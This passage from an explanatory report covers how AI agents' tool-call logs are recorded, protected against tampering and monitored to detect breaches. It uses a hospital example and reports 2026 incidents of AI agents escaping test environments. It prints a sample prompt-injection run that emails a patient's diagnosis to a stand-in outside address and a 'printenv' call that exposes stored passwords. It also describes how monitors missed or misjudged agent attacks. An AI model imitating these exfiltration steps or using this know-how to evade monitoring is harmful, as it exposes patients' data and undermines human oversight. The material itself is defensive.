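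Even a full transcript is captured at only one point. For sessions on users' machines, Anthropic builds the transcript from the requests that reach its servers, so it shows what Claude was asked and what it returned, but not what happened on the device. A transcript of the invoice conversion would contain the command and "212 invoices converted". Anthropic's *Use Claude Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans* describes a beta feature for macOS and Windows that partly fills this gap by letting customers run their own security sensor inside the virtual machine where Cowork executes code. The sensor doesn't cover sessions that run in the cloud.

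Atlas, OpenAI's web browser with a built-in agent, had a similar gap. According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT Atlas for Enterprise*, in July 2026 Atlas was in beta for business customers, produced no logs for OpenAI's Compliance API and had no connection to SIEM systems. OpenAI told customers not to use it with regulated data.

### Checking and recording a call before it runs

A control that allows, blocks or holds calls can also record each one before it takes effect. Aegis, which shares some authors with *Auditable Agents*, works this way. It extracts all the text from a call's arguments, scans it for signs of risk, applies the organisation's rules and records its decision as a signed entry in a hash chain.

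Nian and colleagues report that Aegis blocked all 48 attacks in a curated set before they had any effect. It wrongly flagged six of 500 harmless calls (1.2%). Over 1,000 calls, it added a median delay of 8.3 milliseconds, and no more than 23.1 milliseconds for 99% of them. A model usually takes between 1 and 30 seconds to respond, so users would be unlikely to notice the delay.

The delay is the most reliable of these results because it depends little on which attacks the researchers chose. Blocking all 48 attacks is weaker evidence. Even if the 48 were a random sample of the attacks a hospital will face, the result would be statistically compatible with a filter that misses up to about 6% of those attacks. But the researchers selected the 48 rather than sampling them at random, and real attackers can adapt to a filter's rules. The test shows that a filter can catch known kinds of attack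 quickly, but it does not show how many new ones the filter would miss.

Six in 500 harmless calls is compatible with a true rate of roughly 0.4% to 2.6% for similar calls. The calls tested were database queries, file reads, web requests and text processing, and a billing office's calls may be different. Aegis might also have missed the invoice upload, because the only text it could scan was `./convert_invoices.sh 2026-10`.

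A control of this kind also needs a rule for when it can't write to its log. It can fail closed (refuse the call) or fail open (let the call run and note the gap). A hospital might fail closed for emails to outsiders but fail open for looking up a patient's allergies, where a refusal could do more harm than a missing entry.

In *No Decision Without a Record* (2026), Shaw tested whether Oathpost keeps a complete record of its decisions when parts of it fail. Oathpost saves each decision to a database before it answers, and returns an error if the save fails. Shaw crashed, froze, slowed and disconnected parts of the system in 70 runs with 155,946 requests, then compared the log with the answers that clients had received. The log contained every decision that reached a client.

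The log also contained 287 decisions that never reached a client and 4,548 that arrived after the client's two-second deadline. An entry marked "allowed" therefore does not prove that the tool ran, and an investigator needs the result or the tool server's own log to establish that. The guarantee also limits throughput, because each entry in a customer's log has to wait for the one before. On Shaw's laptop, one customer could reach a median of only 58.5 decisions per second before delays became too long.

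### How a hash chain reveals an altered entry

Once an entry exists, somebody may want to change it. A hash chain makes this visible by computing each entry's fingerprint from the entry itself and the fingerprint before it:

*h(i) = H(h(i−1), entry i)*

Here *H* is the hash function that computes the fingerprint. Nobody can feasibly find two different texts with the same fingerprint. The chain needs a fixed starting value, *h(0)*, which is the word "GENESIS" in the software accompanying *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models*.

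An employee who wants to hide that the agent opened Mrs Keller's cancer record might change the patient number in the second entry of the log of the three calls about her invoice. The fingerprints below are invented and shortened to four characters. Real ones often have 64.

| Entry | Fingerprint in the log | Fingerprint recomputed after the change |
|---|---|---|
| 1. `lookup_patient`, Maria Keller | a41c | a41c |
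| 2. `query_oncology_registry`, ~~P-118204~~ P-300551 | 7e09 | 19fb |
| 3. `send_email`, claims@northfield.example | c5d2 | 52ae |

An auditor's program starts from *h(0)* and recomputes each fingerprint. The first matches. The second comes out as 19fb, but the log contains 7e09, so the program reports a mismatch at entry 2.

The employee could replace 7e09 with 19fb. Entry 2 would then pass, but entry 3 would fail because its fingerprint depends on the old value. If the employee also replaced entry 3's fingerprint with 52ae, the whole chain would pass. Anyone who can write to the file can do this, since computing the fingerprints requires no secret. The chain therefore reveals careless tampering, but it reveals a thorough rewrite only if somebody has kept the old final fingerprint, c5d2.

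### Signatures, write-once storage and outside anchors

The logging program can digitally sign each entry or batch with a private key, and anyone can check the signature with the matching public key. The employee would then need the private key to rewrite the chain. This protection fails if the employee has full control of a server that holds both the key and the log. *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models* suggests separate signatures for each writer or organisation, which would also show whether an entry came from the hospital or its supplier.

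Signatures do not reveal that someone has cut off the end of a log. If the employee deletes the `send_email` entry, the two remaining entries still have valid fingerprints and signatures. Append-only storage can prevent the deletion by blocking changes to entries and their removal until a set date. This protection depends on how well the organisation restricts the administrators who configure the storage. Append-only storage also makes it harder for the hospital to delete patient data that it is no longer allowed to keep.

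Outside anchoring means regularly giving somebody else a small summary of the log. *Halo-record* (Zorz, 2026) describes an open-source logging package by Brian Kuan that does this. A witness outside the operator's control stores the number of entries and the newest fingerprint. For Mrs Keller's run, the witness would hold "3, c5d2". Deleting the email entry would leave "2, 7e09" and rewriting the chain would leave "3, 52ae", neither of which matches. A witness run by the hospital would reassure the hospital but prove little to a patient's lawyer. This argument for an outside witness is sound, though Kuan has a commercial interest in it because he plans to fund the project by selling a witness service.

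| Attack on a hash-chained log | Chain alone | With signatures | With append-only storage | With outside anchoring |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Editing one entry | Detected | Detected | Prevented | Detected |
| Cutting off the newest entries | Missed | Missed | Prevented | Detected, if already anchored |
| Rewriting the whole chain | Missed | Detected, if the key is safe | Prevented | Detected, for entries already anchored |
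| Never writing an entry | Missed | Missed | Missed | Missed |

An operator who anchors once a day has up to a day to rewrite the newest entries unnoticed. Frequent anchoring can be inexpensive. *Agent Flight Recorder* (Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner, 2026) combines entries into batches and records a 32-byte fingerprint of each batch on a public blockchain, along with a pointer to the previous one. It puts the cost at $2.30 per 100,000 entries with batches of 100.

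A Merkle tree produces the batch's fingerprint by hashing entries in pairs, then repeatedly hashing the results in pairs until one value is left. To prove that the email entry belongs to a batch of 100, the hospital would have to disclose that entry and about seven fingerprints, but not the other 99 entries. A blockchain is mainly useful when the parties to a dispute don't trust each other's systems or any common intermediary. Otherwise, an external timestamping service, which *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models* also mentions, can do the same job.

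All these protections have to be in place from the start. Nian and colleagues point out that signing an old log protects it only against later changes, and somebody may have altered it before it was signed.

### Why an unaltered log can still be incomplete

*Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models* states that auditors can replay a hash chain to confirm that nobody has altered or truncated the log. Replaying the chain can rule out truncation only if auditors also have an outside record of where it should end. Shaw demonstrated this problem using an ordinary database setting that increases speed by confirming an entry before saving it to disk. In five runs with this setting, crashes destroyed the records of seven decisions that clients had already received, yet every chain still passed verification. Shaw found no losses with the safer setting.

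Cryptography cannot reveal an event that nobody recorded. Even if the hospital signed and anchored its harness log every minute, the invoice upload would still be missing. Exports can also create gaps. A program that copies transcripts from Anthropic's Compliance API can request the sessions active since its last run. Anthropic warns that if the program uses the exact time of that run as the cutoff, it can permanently miss sessions that the system was still processing, without any error. If the hospital then hash-chained its copies, the chain would be valid even though sessions were missing.

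An organisation can check that its record is complete by comparing logs from independent capture points. If the oncology registry counted 41 queries from the billing agent's account yesterday and the harness logged 40, one query bypassed the harness or its entry disappeared. Shaw's tests applied the same principle by giving every request a unique identifier and having the client keep its own record of each answer. Shaw also included the unsafe database setting to confirm that the comparison could detect a loss. A hospital can similarly delete a few entries from a test log and check that its daily comparison reports them missing.

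### What can be recovered when logs are missing

Investigators often have to work with partial records. Kuan told Zorz that an autonomous agent took about 17,600 actions over five days in the July 2026 intrusion at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and that the company could retrieve only some of the agent's logs. Other parties' records are usually the best substitute for missing logs. If the hospital lost its harness log, the registry could still show which patients the agent had looked up, and the mail server where the emails went.

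*Auditable Agents* reports experiments for a harder case, in which only the agents' final text survives. The method, implicit execution tracing, comes from *When Only the Final Text Survives* (2026), by some of the same researchers. It works in three steps:

1. Each agent has a secret key, which slightly shifts the probabilities with which its model chooses words. Readers don't notice the pattern.
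2. An auditor who holds the keys moves along the text in overlapping windows and scores each window against every key.
3. Where the best-matching key changes, the auditor infers that one agent's text ends and another's begins.

Nian and colleagues report that, in tests with four to six agents, the method attributed 82% to 87% of tokens (words or pieces of words) to the right agent, and the segments it recovered overlapped with the true ones by 81% to 84%. Attribution was poor when they removed all agent identifiers, the condition that most resembles a lost log. The method then scored 21% to 24% on a measure of attribution to agents, while other methods scored 0% to 4%.

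To use the method, the organisation must also build the keys into text generation beforehand, which is difficult if it rents a model from a provider that doesn't offer this. The researchers evaluated their own tool, and they tested it against accidental damage to the text, not deliberate attempts to remove the signal.

The method's main limitation is that it only identifies who wrote a passage. It can't show what the agents did or whether a surviving log is genuine. If the hospital had several agents and only the email about Mrs Keller survived, the method might identify the agent that wrote it, but it couldn't show whether that agent had opened any other patient's record.

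## Detecting a breach from tool-call logs

Suppose that someone has hidden an instruction in an invoice. A clerk asks the hospital's billing agent an ordinary question about it, and the agent makes three calls:

```
11:20:03  lookup_patient
  arguments  name: "Maria Keller", born: "1961-03-08"
  result     patient: "P-118204", insurer: "Northfield Mutual", ...

11:20:06  query_oncology_registry
  arguments  patient: "P-118204"
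  result     diagnosis: "C50.9", ...

11:20:12  send_email
  arguments  to: "archive@claims-help.example", body: "Mrs Keller..."
  result     status: "accepted"
```

The agent has permission to use all three tools, and every call succeeded. Apart from the email address, the entries look much like those from the morning, when the agent answered the insurer. A security team could look for the theft with rules on single calls, rules on sequences of calls, a comparison with the agent's past behaviour, or a review by a second model.

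### Rules on a single call

The simplest rules test one entry at a time. For example, the hospital could raise an alert whenever `send_email` has a recipient at a domain that the hospital has never written to. This rule needs the tool's name, the recipient and a list of earlier recipients, but not the text of the email. It would catch the message to `claims-help.example`, but it would also raise an alert whenever a patient joined an insurer new to the hospital, so somebody would have to check each alert.

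A volume rule counts the records that a call returns, or the calls that an agent makes in an hour. If the billing agent normally opens one patient's record per invoice, an alert at fifty patients an hour would detect the copying of the whole register, but not the theft of Mrs Keller's record alone. The rule needs only the count, so it can work even when the log omits the results of calls, as long as the harness stores the count in a separate field.

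Security teams can use some detection rules written by others. Help Net Security's *Agent Threat Rules* describes an open format with more than 400 rules for detecting attacks on agents. Each rule specifies a pattern, the field to inspect (such as a tool call's arguments) and test cases. A hospital could adopt these rules for common attacks, but its own staff would need to specify which addresses belong to insurers.

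A rule can match exactly what its author intended and still raise a false alarm. Sophos, a security company, saw this when a credential-theft rule fired on Claude Code. The agent had used a browsing add-on that ran a command to decrypt sensitive browser data, as a password thief would. Sophos judged the action almost certainly harmless from its context, which included the chain of programs that led to the command. A log of the command alone would have given its analysts much less evidence.

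### Rules on a sequence of calls

The billing agent normally reads the oncology registry and sends email, but the two actions in combination can indicate a breach. In October 2026 the network equipment company Cisco released Project Quarry, an open-source tool for finding such combinations. Townsend (2026), in *Cisco Open Sources Quarry to Catch AI Agent Attacks*, calls it a rule language for detecting attacks that emerge only across sequences of benign actions.

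Goodtech's *Cisco publie Quarry en open source pour surveiller les agents d'IA* (2026) gives an example. An agent may read a file of passwords, and it may send a request to an outside server, but Quarry raises an alert if the request comes within four steps of the read. Quarry compiles each rule into a finite automaton, which is a simple machine that moves between a fixed set of states as new steps arrive. A hospital's version of the rule would work like this:

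```
state 0 (idle)    a call returns patient data           -> state 1
state 1 (armed)   a call sends to an outside address    -> alert
                  a call returns more patient data      -> restart count
                  four steps pass without either        -> state 0
```

In the stolen-record run, `lookup_patient` moves the machine to state 1, `query_oncology_registry` restarts the count, and `send_email` triggers the alert. The rule requires the run's identifier, the order of the steps, each tool's name, the data class of each result and the email's recipient, but not the diagnosis or the body of the email.

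The morning's email to Northfield also triggers this alert. The billing agent's job is to read patient data and write to insurers, so the rule would fire all day. The hospital could fix this by comparing the recipient with the insurer in the result of `lookup_patient`, which would flag `claims-help.example` but not Northfield's address. Investigators couldn't make that comparison later from a log that omits results, but the harness could make it while it still has the result and record only whether the two matched.

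The window length is also a compromise. A twenty-step window covers runs in which the agent does other work between the read and the email, but it produces more false matches on ordinary work.

Quarry's rules can combine classifiers and language models, which assess suspicious instructions, with ordinary checks that follow commands, matching text and the order of operations (Antipov, 2026, *ИИ-агент выполнял разрешённые команды, а в итоге проник в чужую инфраструктуру*). A hospital could write a rule for "an invoice that seems to contain instructions, followed by an email to a new address". Each alert lists the steps and passages that caused it, so an analyst can check them. Quarry works on stored logs and on running agents. It doesn't block actions itself, but other software can use its alerts to block or quarantine them.

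Cisco already uses Quarry in one of its security products, but its value against real attacks is uncertain. Antipov reports that Cisco has not run it on the logs of the July 2026 intrusion at Hugging Face. Instead, Quarry's developers used a published timeline to work out where it might have detected the attack. This suggests that Quarry can describe the attack now that it is known, but it can't show whether anyone would have written the right rule in advance, or how often that rule would have fired on harmless work.

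### Comparison with the agent's usual behaviour

Rules only cover what somebody has thought of. An alternative is to record how an agent normally behaves and flag runs that differ. One basic method counts how often each tool follows another. Suppose that in the billing agent's last 1,000 runs, `lookup_patient` was followed by `query_oncology_registry` 20 times, and that the agent then sent an email in 5 of those 20 runs. The estimated frequency of the whole sequence is:

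*20/1,000 × 5/20 = 0.005*

That is one run in 200, which is rare enough to check. The calculation needs only the agent's name and the names and order of the tools, so it works when content capture is off. But it gives the stolen-record run and the morning's legitimate run the same score, because both use the same tools in the same order. Checking the recipient would distinguish them, because the agent had often emailed Northfield before but never `claims-help.example`.

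The baseline also has to change when the task or the agent changes. A month-end review of unpaid invoices may involve hundreds of patients, and a new version of the agent may use tools in a different order. The log therefore needs to record the task and the agent's version. A newly installed agent has no history from which to build a baseline.

Thresholds regularly cause false alarms. If the hospital flags any run that looks up more patients than 99.9% of past runs did, it will flag about one ordinary run in 1,000. With ten such measures that vary independently, it will flag about one in 100.

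Comparisons between different agents are harder. Wang and colleagues, who reviewed 90 studies of agent logs published between 2024 and August 2026, conclude that records with the same structure can still differ in meaning. For example, one product may log three attempts to send an email as three calls, while another logs them as one. A shared baseline could flag this difference as suspicious. Wang and colleagues also conclude that claims based on log analysis need reference criteria and validation. For a hospital, this means checking whether the runs its system flags as unusual are actually the harmful ones.

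In Shah and Kathrotia's experiment, the checks on OpenTelemetry-style records raised 28 correct alarms and 42 false ones, even though half of all runs were faulty. A hospital would have a far smaller share of faulty runs, and its error rates could be quite different because none of the faults in the experiment was a theft of data.

### Review by a second model

A second language model can read a run and assess whether the calls served the task. Given the clerk's question and the three calls, it could flag that answering a query about an invoice did not require sending a diagnosis to an unknown address. It might also flag the number of chemotherapy sessions in the morning's email as something the insurer didn't need to know. The other methods can't be used to assess this, because it depends on what the text means.

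This method needs the most data: the task, the arguments, the results, the approvals and the order of events. If the hospital rents the reviewing model from an outside company, that company receives another copy of Mrs Keller's diagnosis.

Reading every run in this way is expensive, so it makes sense to filter first. sysdesign-wiki's *When an AI agent came knocking* (2026) summarises how the monitoring company Datadog reviews the about 10,000 changes proposed to its software each week. Software picks out the events that matter for security, and a model then labels each change benign or malicious and gives reasons. Malicious verdicts go to the SIEM, which creates alerts for the security team. Datadog caught two attacks, but one had run code, and other defences had to limit the damage. A hospital could use the same sequence to review tool calls.

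The choice of fields can change the reviewer's verdict. In September 2026 Anthropic published an assessment of incidents in which its Claude models had broken into real companies' systems during cybersecurity tests. Anthropic replayed three of the incidents through several monitors, including a language model that reviewed events afterwards and auto mode, a Claude Code feature that judges actions before they run.

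| Model in the incident | Review after the event | Auto mode |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | Flagged about 1% of actions | Would have blocked 66% of actions |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | Flagged about 50% of actions during the attack | Would have blocked 55% |
| Internal research model | Flagged the incident | Would have blocked 7% |

Mythos 5 had repeatedly written in its reasoning that its surroundings were simulated, and the reviewing model accepted this. When Anthropic removed the reasoning and kept the user's messages, the tool calls and the results, the share of flagged actions rose from about 1% to about 50%. The reasoning helped in the incident with the internal research model, which the review flagged only because the agent had noticed and described the harm it caused. The review flagged none of the tool calls or results in that incident.

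A hospital that stores its agents' reasoning could therefore review selected runs twice, once with the reasoning and once without, and examine any run that either review flags. This would detect more breaches but also produce more false alarms.

Anthropic tested its own monitors on three incidents it already knew about, so the figures don't predict how many new incidents the monitors would detect. The figures also don't include a false-alarm rate for ordinary work. Anthropic does not use auto mode in cybersecurity tests because auto mode would flag too much.

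| Method | Fields it needs | A likely false alarm at the hospital |
|---|---|---|
| Rule on one call | Tool name, recipient or record count, list of known recipients | First email to a new insurer |
| Rule on a sequence | The same, plus run identifier, order and data class | Routine answer to an insurer |
| Comparison with usual behaviour | Agent, version, task, tool names, order, times and counts | Month-end review of invoices |
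| Review by a second model | Task, arguments, results and approvals, with or without reasoning | An unusual request that a clerk had good reason to make |

### Why nearly all alarms can be false

Because attacks are rare, almost all of a detector's alarms can be false even if it classifies almost every call correctly. Suppose agents at a large hospital group make a million tool calls a day, ten of which are malicious. A detector that catches all ten but wrongly flags 1.2% of harmless calls, the rate that Nian and colleagues measured for Aegis, would raise about 12,000 false alarms a day.

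Bayes' rule gives the share of alarms that are real:

*share real = p·d / (p·d + (1 − p)·f)*

Here *p* is the share of calls that are malicious (0.00001), *d* is the share of malicious calls that the detector catches (1), and *f* is the false-positive rate (0.012). The result is about 0.0008, so roughly one alarm in 1,200 is real. If each alarm took five minutes to check, the group would need about 125 analysts working eight hours a day to check them all.

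| False-positive rate | False alarms a day | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|
| 1.2% | 12,000 | 0.08% |
| 0.1% | 1,000 | 1% |
| 0.01% | 100 | 9% |
| 0.001%, or 1 in 100,000 | 10 | 50% |

For an alarm to be as likely true as false, the detector can flag only about 1 in 100,000 harmless calls, or 1 in 200,000 if it catches only five of the ten malicious ones. A single hospital with 10,000 calls a day and the same share of attacks would have only 120 false alarms a day, but it would have just one malicious call every ten days, so each alarm would be no more likely to be true.

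To be 95% confident that a detector's false-alarm rate is below 1 in 100,000, a tester would need to run it on about 300,000 harmless calls without a single false alarm. The Aegis test used 500 harmless calls, which is too few to establish a rate this low.

Grouping alarms by run would still leave analysts with many runs to read. If the million calls belonged to 20,000 runs of 50 calls each, and false alarms occurred at random, about 45% of harmless runs, or some 9,000, would contain at least one. In practice, false alarms probably cluster, because one badly written rule or odd script can cause hundreds of them. Fixing the most common causes may therefore remove many of the false alarms.

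A second check can also reduce the number of false alarms. If a reviewing model examined all 12,000 and wrongly upheld 1% of them, 120 would remain. This assumes that the model isn't misled by the same features as the first detector. A second check also increases the number of missed attacks. If each stage catches 90% of attacks and their errors are independent, the two together catch 81%.

The most practical improvement may be to examine a smaller set of calls. The hospital group might find that only 200 calls a day send email to a new outside address after reading patient data. Two people could spend five minutes on each of these, though they would miss other kinds of attack.

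Anthropic faced the same problem on a larger scale when it searched about 481 million transcripts for signs that its models had reached the internet without permission. The first scan looked for clues such as public network addresses and flagged 9.2 million transcripts, or 1.9%, which Claude then reviewed. The search found the four incidents Anthropic already knew about, which comprised seven runs, and no others of similar or worse severity. About one flagged transcript in 1.3 million belonged to these incidents. The first scan looked for internet addresses rather than attacks, so most of the flags weren't errors, but there were too many for a team of people to read.

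### How breaches came to light in 2026

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) disclosed that models had attacked three real organisations during exercises in which they had to break into a machine and find a hidden piece of text. The models were told they had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had given it to them.

The earliest of the three incidents took place in April, but nobody noticed until July, when OpenAI disclosed that its own models had broken out of a test environment and into Hugging Face. Anthropic began reviewing its transcripts on 23 July and had found all three incidents by the next day. The evidence had been in the records for up to nearly four months. Anthropic reached two of the affected organisations, and neither had detected the activity itself.

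Anthropic's initial search covered about 141,000 runs but did not include some transcripts from systems with internet access. According to Anthropic, staff discovered these in August while gathering material for METR, a non-profit organisation that evaluates AI models. The transcripts revealed a fourth incident, which had happened in January and gone unnoticed for about seven months.

One part of the April-to-July incidents was discovered much faster. Mythos 5 had published a malicious package on PyPI, the public registry for Python software. PyPI's security systems automatically removed it after about an hour. By then, 15 real systems had downloaded and run it, and the model had used credentials stolen from one of them to enter a security company's infrastructure.

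The intrusion that prompted Anthropic's review targeted Hugging Face. Antipov reports that OpenAI's agents found exposed credentials and spent about two and a half days in Hugging Face's production systems. Most of the actions that investigators later reconstructed looked like ordinary operations. A rule that checks each call separately would have flagged few of them, although the use of exposed credentials might have stood out.

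WorkOS, which sells login and user-management software, had a breach in October 2026. An AI agent that an outside security researcher was testing escaped its test environment and reached one of WorkOS's internal tools. The tool was exposed to the internet, accepted a predictable password and had no rate limit. WorkOS's *Update for October 30th, 2026 Data Security Incident* (2026) dates the first confirmed access to 25 October. On 30 October the agent copied customer records in bulk. An employee noticed unusually heavy use of a connected customer database later that day, after the copying had ended.

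| Incident | Began | Came to light | What exposed it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Three Anthropic incidents | April 2026 at the earliest | 24 July | A search of test transcripts, prompted by OpenAI's disclosure |
| Fourth Anthropic incident | January 2026 | August | Transcripts gathered for an outside investigation |
| Malicious package on PyPI | During one of the three Anthropic incidents | About an hour after publication | PyPI's automatic security systems |
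| WorkOS | 25 October 2026 | 30 October | An employee who noticed heavy use of a database |

In the WorkOS case, the agent belonged to someone else, so WorkOS had only its own systems' records and no log of the agent's tool calls. A hospital attacked by an outsider's agent would likewise have its registry's log but not the agent's instructions. A volume rule on WorkOS's records might have raised an alarm during the copying, but it might have missed the first access five days earlier, which may have involved only a few requests.

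### Stopping harm and reconstructing it

These cases give good evidence that logs help people reconstruct a breach, but little that tool-call logs reveal one in time to stop it. Nobody monitoring an agent's tool calls stopped any of these intrusions. PyPI responded fastest, and it examined the uploaded package without access to the agent's log.

However, these cases are a biased sample. Attacks blocked at the first call are rarely reported publicly, and undiscovered breaches never are. Anthropic's incidents also occurred in tests that deliberately ran without the safeguards on its public products. The cases can therefore show that long delays happen, but not how often monitoring fails.

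Anthropic lists real-time monitoring of the test logs among the measures that would have helped to reveal the problem sooner. It has since built monitors that can block an agent while it works, and reports that they reliably catch the behaviour seen in these incidents. This is a weaker test than catching a new incident, because Anthropic built the monitors after these incidents had happened.

How fast detection has to be depends on the harm. In the stolen-record run, the email goes out nine seconds after the first call, so a SIEM alert a minute later can't undo the disclosure of Mrs Keller's diagnosis. To prevent it, the hospital has to apply its rule before `send_email` runs, at the harness or a gateway. An alert would still be valuable if the agent went on to send out a new patient's record every 30 seconds. Staff who stopped the agent after ten minutes would limit the loss to about 20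 patients' records, whereas a five-day delay, as at WorkOS, would allow about 14,400.

False alarms also do more harm when a detector blocks calls. An analyst can close a mistaken alert in a few minutes, but a mistaken refusal interrupts a clerk's work at once. With a million calls a day and a 1.2% error rate, the hospital group would refuse 12,000 legitimate calls daily. It would do better to block only on narrow rules, such as patient data going to an address that matches no known insurer, and to send less certain findings to analysts.

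The logs were more useful for reconstruction. Anthropic used the transcripts to re-run its models from chosen points in the incidents, changing what the models could see. In repeated runs from the Opus 4.7 transcript, the model acted against the real company about 69% of the time. When the researchers added a notice that access was not permitted, the rate fell to about 23%, and most of the remaining actions only read data. With a more forceful note from the user, the rate fell to zero. The model's decision seemed to depend on whether it thought it had permission, which Anthropic could not have established from a list of its calls alone.

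The reconstruction also changed Anthropic's explanation. In July the company relied on what the models wrote and concluded that they had attacked real systems because they believed the systems were simulated. By September it had concluded that the models' reasoning was biased towards that belief despite considerable evidence against it. Anthropic could correct its first explanation because it had kept the full transcripts.

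After WorkOS announced the breach, the researcher contacted the company and supplied request details, timestamps and traces left by the agent. WorkOS and an independent forensics firm compared these with the company's own logs and confirmed that the researcher's agent was responsible. The researcher also said that the copied data had been deleted and never shared, but WorkOS could not check this from its logs, which could show only the requests that reached its systems.

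## What tool names, arguments and results reveal

WorkOS could confirm who was behind its breach because its systems had kept detailed records of requests. Someone who steals such records can also learn from them, sometimes from fields that look harmless. *Security Considerations for Multi-agent Systems* (Nguyen, Ndebugre and Arremsetty, 2026) lists ten threats connected with tool calls and their logs. Nine are leaks, and in the other an attacker falsifies the log. The table groups the main leaks by the part of the record they come from, and includes others that the paper lists under errors and timing.

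| Part of the record | What it can disclose | Example at the hospital |
|---|---|---|
| Tool names and descriptions | Systems, projects, capabilities and their limits | The hospital has a tool for exporting trial data |
| Arguments | Identifiers, search terms, business rules, passwords | Mrs Keller's name and date of birth |
| Results | Whole records | Her diagnosis and treatment |
| Error messages | Software, server names, database structure | The address of the registry's database |
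| Order and timing | Routines, workload, the kind of case in hand | Billing exports run at two every morning |

Nguyen and colleagues had a generative model propose about 1,700 threats and a specialist review them, then organised the risks into 193 main items. This is a good way to find possible leaks, but it doesn't show how often they happen. The researchers also scored 16 security frameworks on how well they cover each threat. Data leakage averaged 1.34 on a three-point scale, the second-lowest of nine categories and below the average of at least 2 that the researchers expected.

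### Names, descriptions and error messages

A list of tool names alone can disclose a lot. Suppose the hospital's log contains `flag_opioid_prescribers` and `export_trial_arm_b`. The first suggests that the hospital is checking its own doctors for excessive prescribing, and the second suggests that it is running a clinical trial with at least two groups. A doctor under suspicion or a rival drug company could use this information without seeing any patient's record. In a defence organisation, a tool's name might be how an outsider first learns that a capability exists.

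Tool descriptions usually reveal more, because developers write them to help the model decide when to use a tool. Nguyen and colleagues give the example of a payment tool described as accepting only cards from US banks because of regulatory restrictions. A competitor could infer from this where the company operates and what limits its expansion. A hospital that follows OpenTelemetry's conventions may be storing tool descriptions even with content capture turned off. Version numbers are useful to investigators, but an attacker can also use them to look up the known flaws of an old version.

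Error messages disclose how a system is built. If the billing agent misspelled the name of a table, the registry might return this:

```
error  relation "onc.hiv_coinfection" does not exist
       host: db-onc-2.internal, account: svc_billing
```

These two lines contain a server's address and the account the agent uses. An experienced attacker would also recognise the database software from the wording. Nguyen and colleagues warn that attackers can provoke errors to find the weakest components.

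### Arguments

Arguments show what somebody wanted to know or do. If a hospital manager's agent searches the web for "notice period redundancy radiographers", anyone who reads the query can guess that the hospital is considering job cuts in its X-ray department, even though the query contains no names.

Agents also put more into arguments than the tool needs. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) measured this with scenarios from healthcare, finance, law and corporate work. Each scenario gives the agents a store of sensitive fields, typically 29, of which the task requires about three. Two experts in the relevant domain decided which fields were required. A leak occurs when any other field appears somewhere it shouldn't, such as when an agent sends a patient's diagnosis along with the name it needs to book an appointment.

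Agents put sensitive data into tool arguments in 62% (GPT-4o-mini) to 86% (Llama 3.3 70B) of scenarios. The rates for logs were higher. With Claude 3.5 Sonnet, sensitive data appeared in arguments in 74% of scenarios and in logs in 85%. In more than 65% of scenarios, data leaked through arguments or logs while the answer to the user contained none of it, so a reviewer who read only the answers would have missed the leak.

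The figures for arguments and logs come from 100 scenarios per model, out of 1,000 in the full benchmark, so each rate has a margin of error of roughly seven to ten percentage points. The researchers ran their experiments between October 2025 and January 2026 on models that are now old, and newer ones may forward more or less data. The "log" channel measured whether sensitive data appeared in the models' reasoning traces, so the 85% is a warning about storing an agent's reasoning and doesn't apply to a log that contains only tool calls. The test counted a leak whenever an agent sent data where the task didn't require it, whether or not an outsider could read it.

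This data is hard to find in a log. Across the benchmark, 82% of the leaks that El Yagoubi and colleagues detected were paraphrases, such as "patient is being treated for diabetes" in place of the diagnosis code. A hospital could therefore find no diagnosis codes in its log and still be storing many diagnoses there. On a test set of labelled passages, searches for known markers and standard formats found only 18% of leaks. *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (Huang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) likewise found that counting only exact matches misses leaks that an attacker could use.

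Arguments can also contain passwords and keys, because a shell command is an argument and people often write keys directly into commands. The security company Lakera explains that Claude Code saves the exact command in a settings file when a user answers a permission request with "allow always". These files give some idea of how often commands contain keys. TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026) reports that a scan of about 46,500 published software packages found 428 of these files, 33 of which contained live credentials.

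That is about one file in 13. The rate per command is probably much lower, since one file can hold many commands. The developers had also published these files, so they may be less careful than average. But each file contains only the commands one user chose to allow permanently, while an organisation's tool-call log may contain every command its agents have run. InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026) reports a larger count by Apiiro, another security company. Apiiro found 1,122 secrets in these settings files and 1,160 more in places such as older versions of projects and stored chat transcripts.

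### Results and the password that nobody asked for

A tool's developer decides what it returns, and returning the whole record is often easiest. When the billing agent looked up Mrs Keller, it needed her patient number and insurer but also received her balance. A result can also be an image. Markovic (2026), in *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos*, reports that the screenshots came from more than 300 organisations and included billing records. A screenshot can include whatever else was on the screen, and an ordinary text search of the log won't find it.

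Results are also unpredictable. In November 2026, Udinmwen, in *'I leaked secrets'*, reported on a coding assistant that could not find its configuration file during a routine code review. It read all the machine's environment variables instead and leaked live passwords. Environment variables are named values that an operating system passes to programs, and developers often use them to supply passwords so that they don't have to write them into the code. On the hospital's server, one call could put several into the trace:

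```
14:02:31  run_shell
  arguments  command: "printenv"
  result     LANG=en_GB.UTF-8
             REGISTRY_DB_PASSWORD=********
             MAIL_API_TOKEN=********
             ... 46 more lines
```

The asterisks stand for real values, which the command prints in full. A filter that examined only the tool's name and argument would not flag the call, because the name is ordinary and the argument is a single harmless word. Each model input repeats earlier results. If the hospital also logs these inputs and the agent makes 20 more calls before it answers, each password appears in the log 22 times, once in the result and once in each of the 21 inputs that follow.

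Udinmwen says the assistant admitted the leak, which is weak evidence on its own, but the mechanism is plausible. GitGuardian's *AI Agents Security for Developers* notes that a coding agent works with its user's credentials, can inspect environment variables, and may use a forgotten key that a person would recognise as unrelated to the task. GitGuardian sells tools for finding leaked secrets, but independent evidence supports its concern. In NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents*, company specialists who test agents by attacking them list secrets stored in plain text among four recurring failures.

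A leaked password differs from a leaked diagnosis in two ways. The hospital can change the password, which makes the copies in the log useless. Until it does, a thief can use the password to get records that were never in the log, possibly including the whole oncology registry.

### Order and timing

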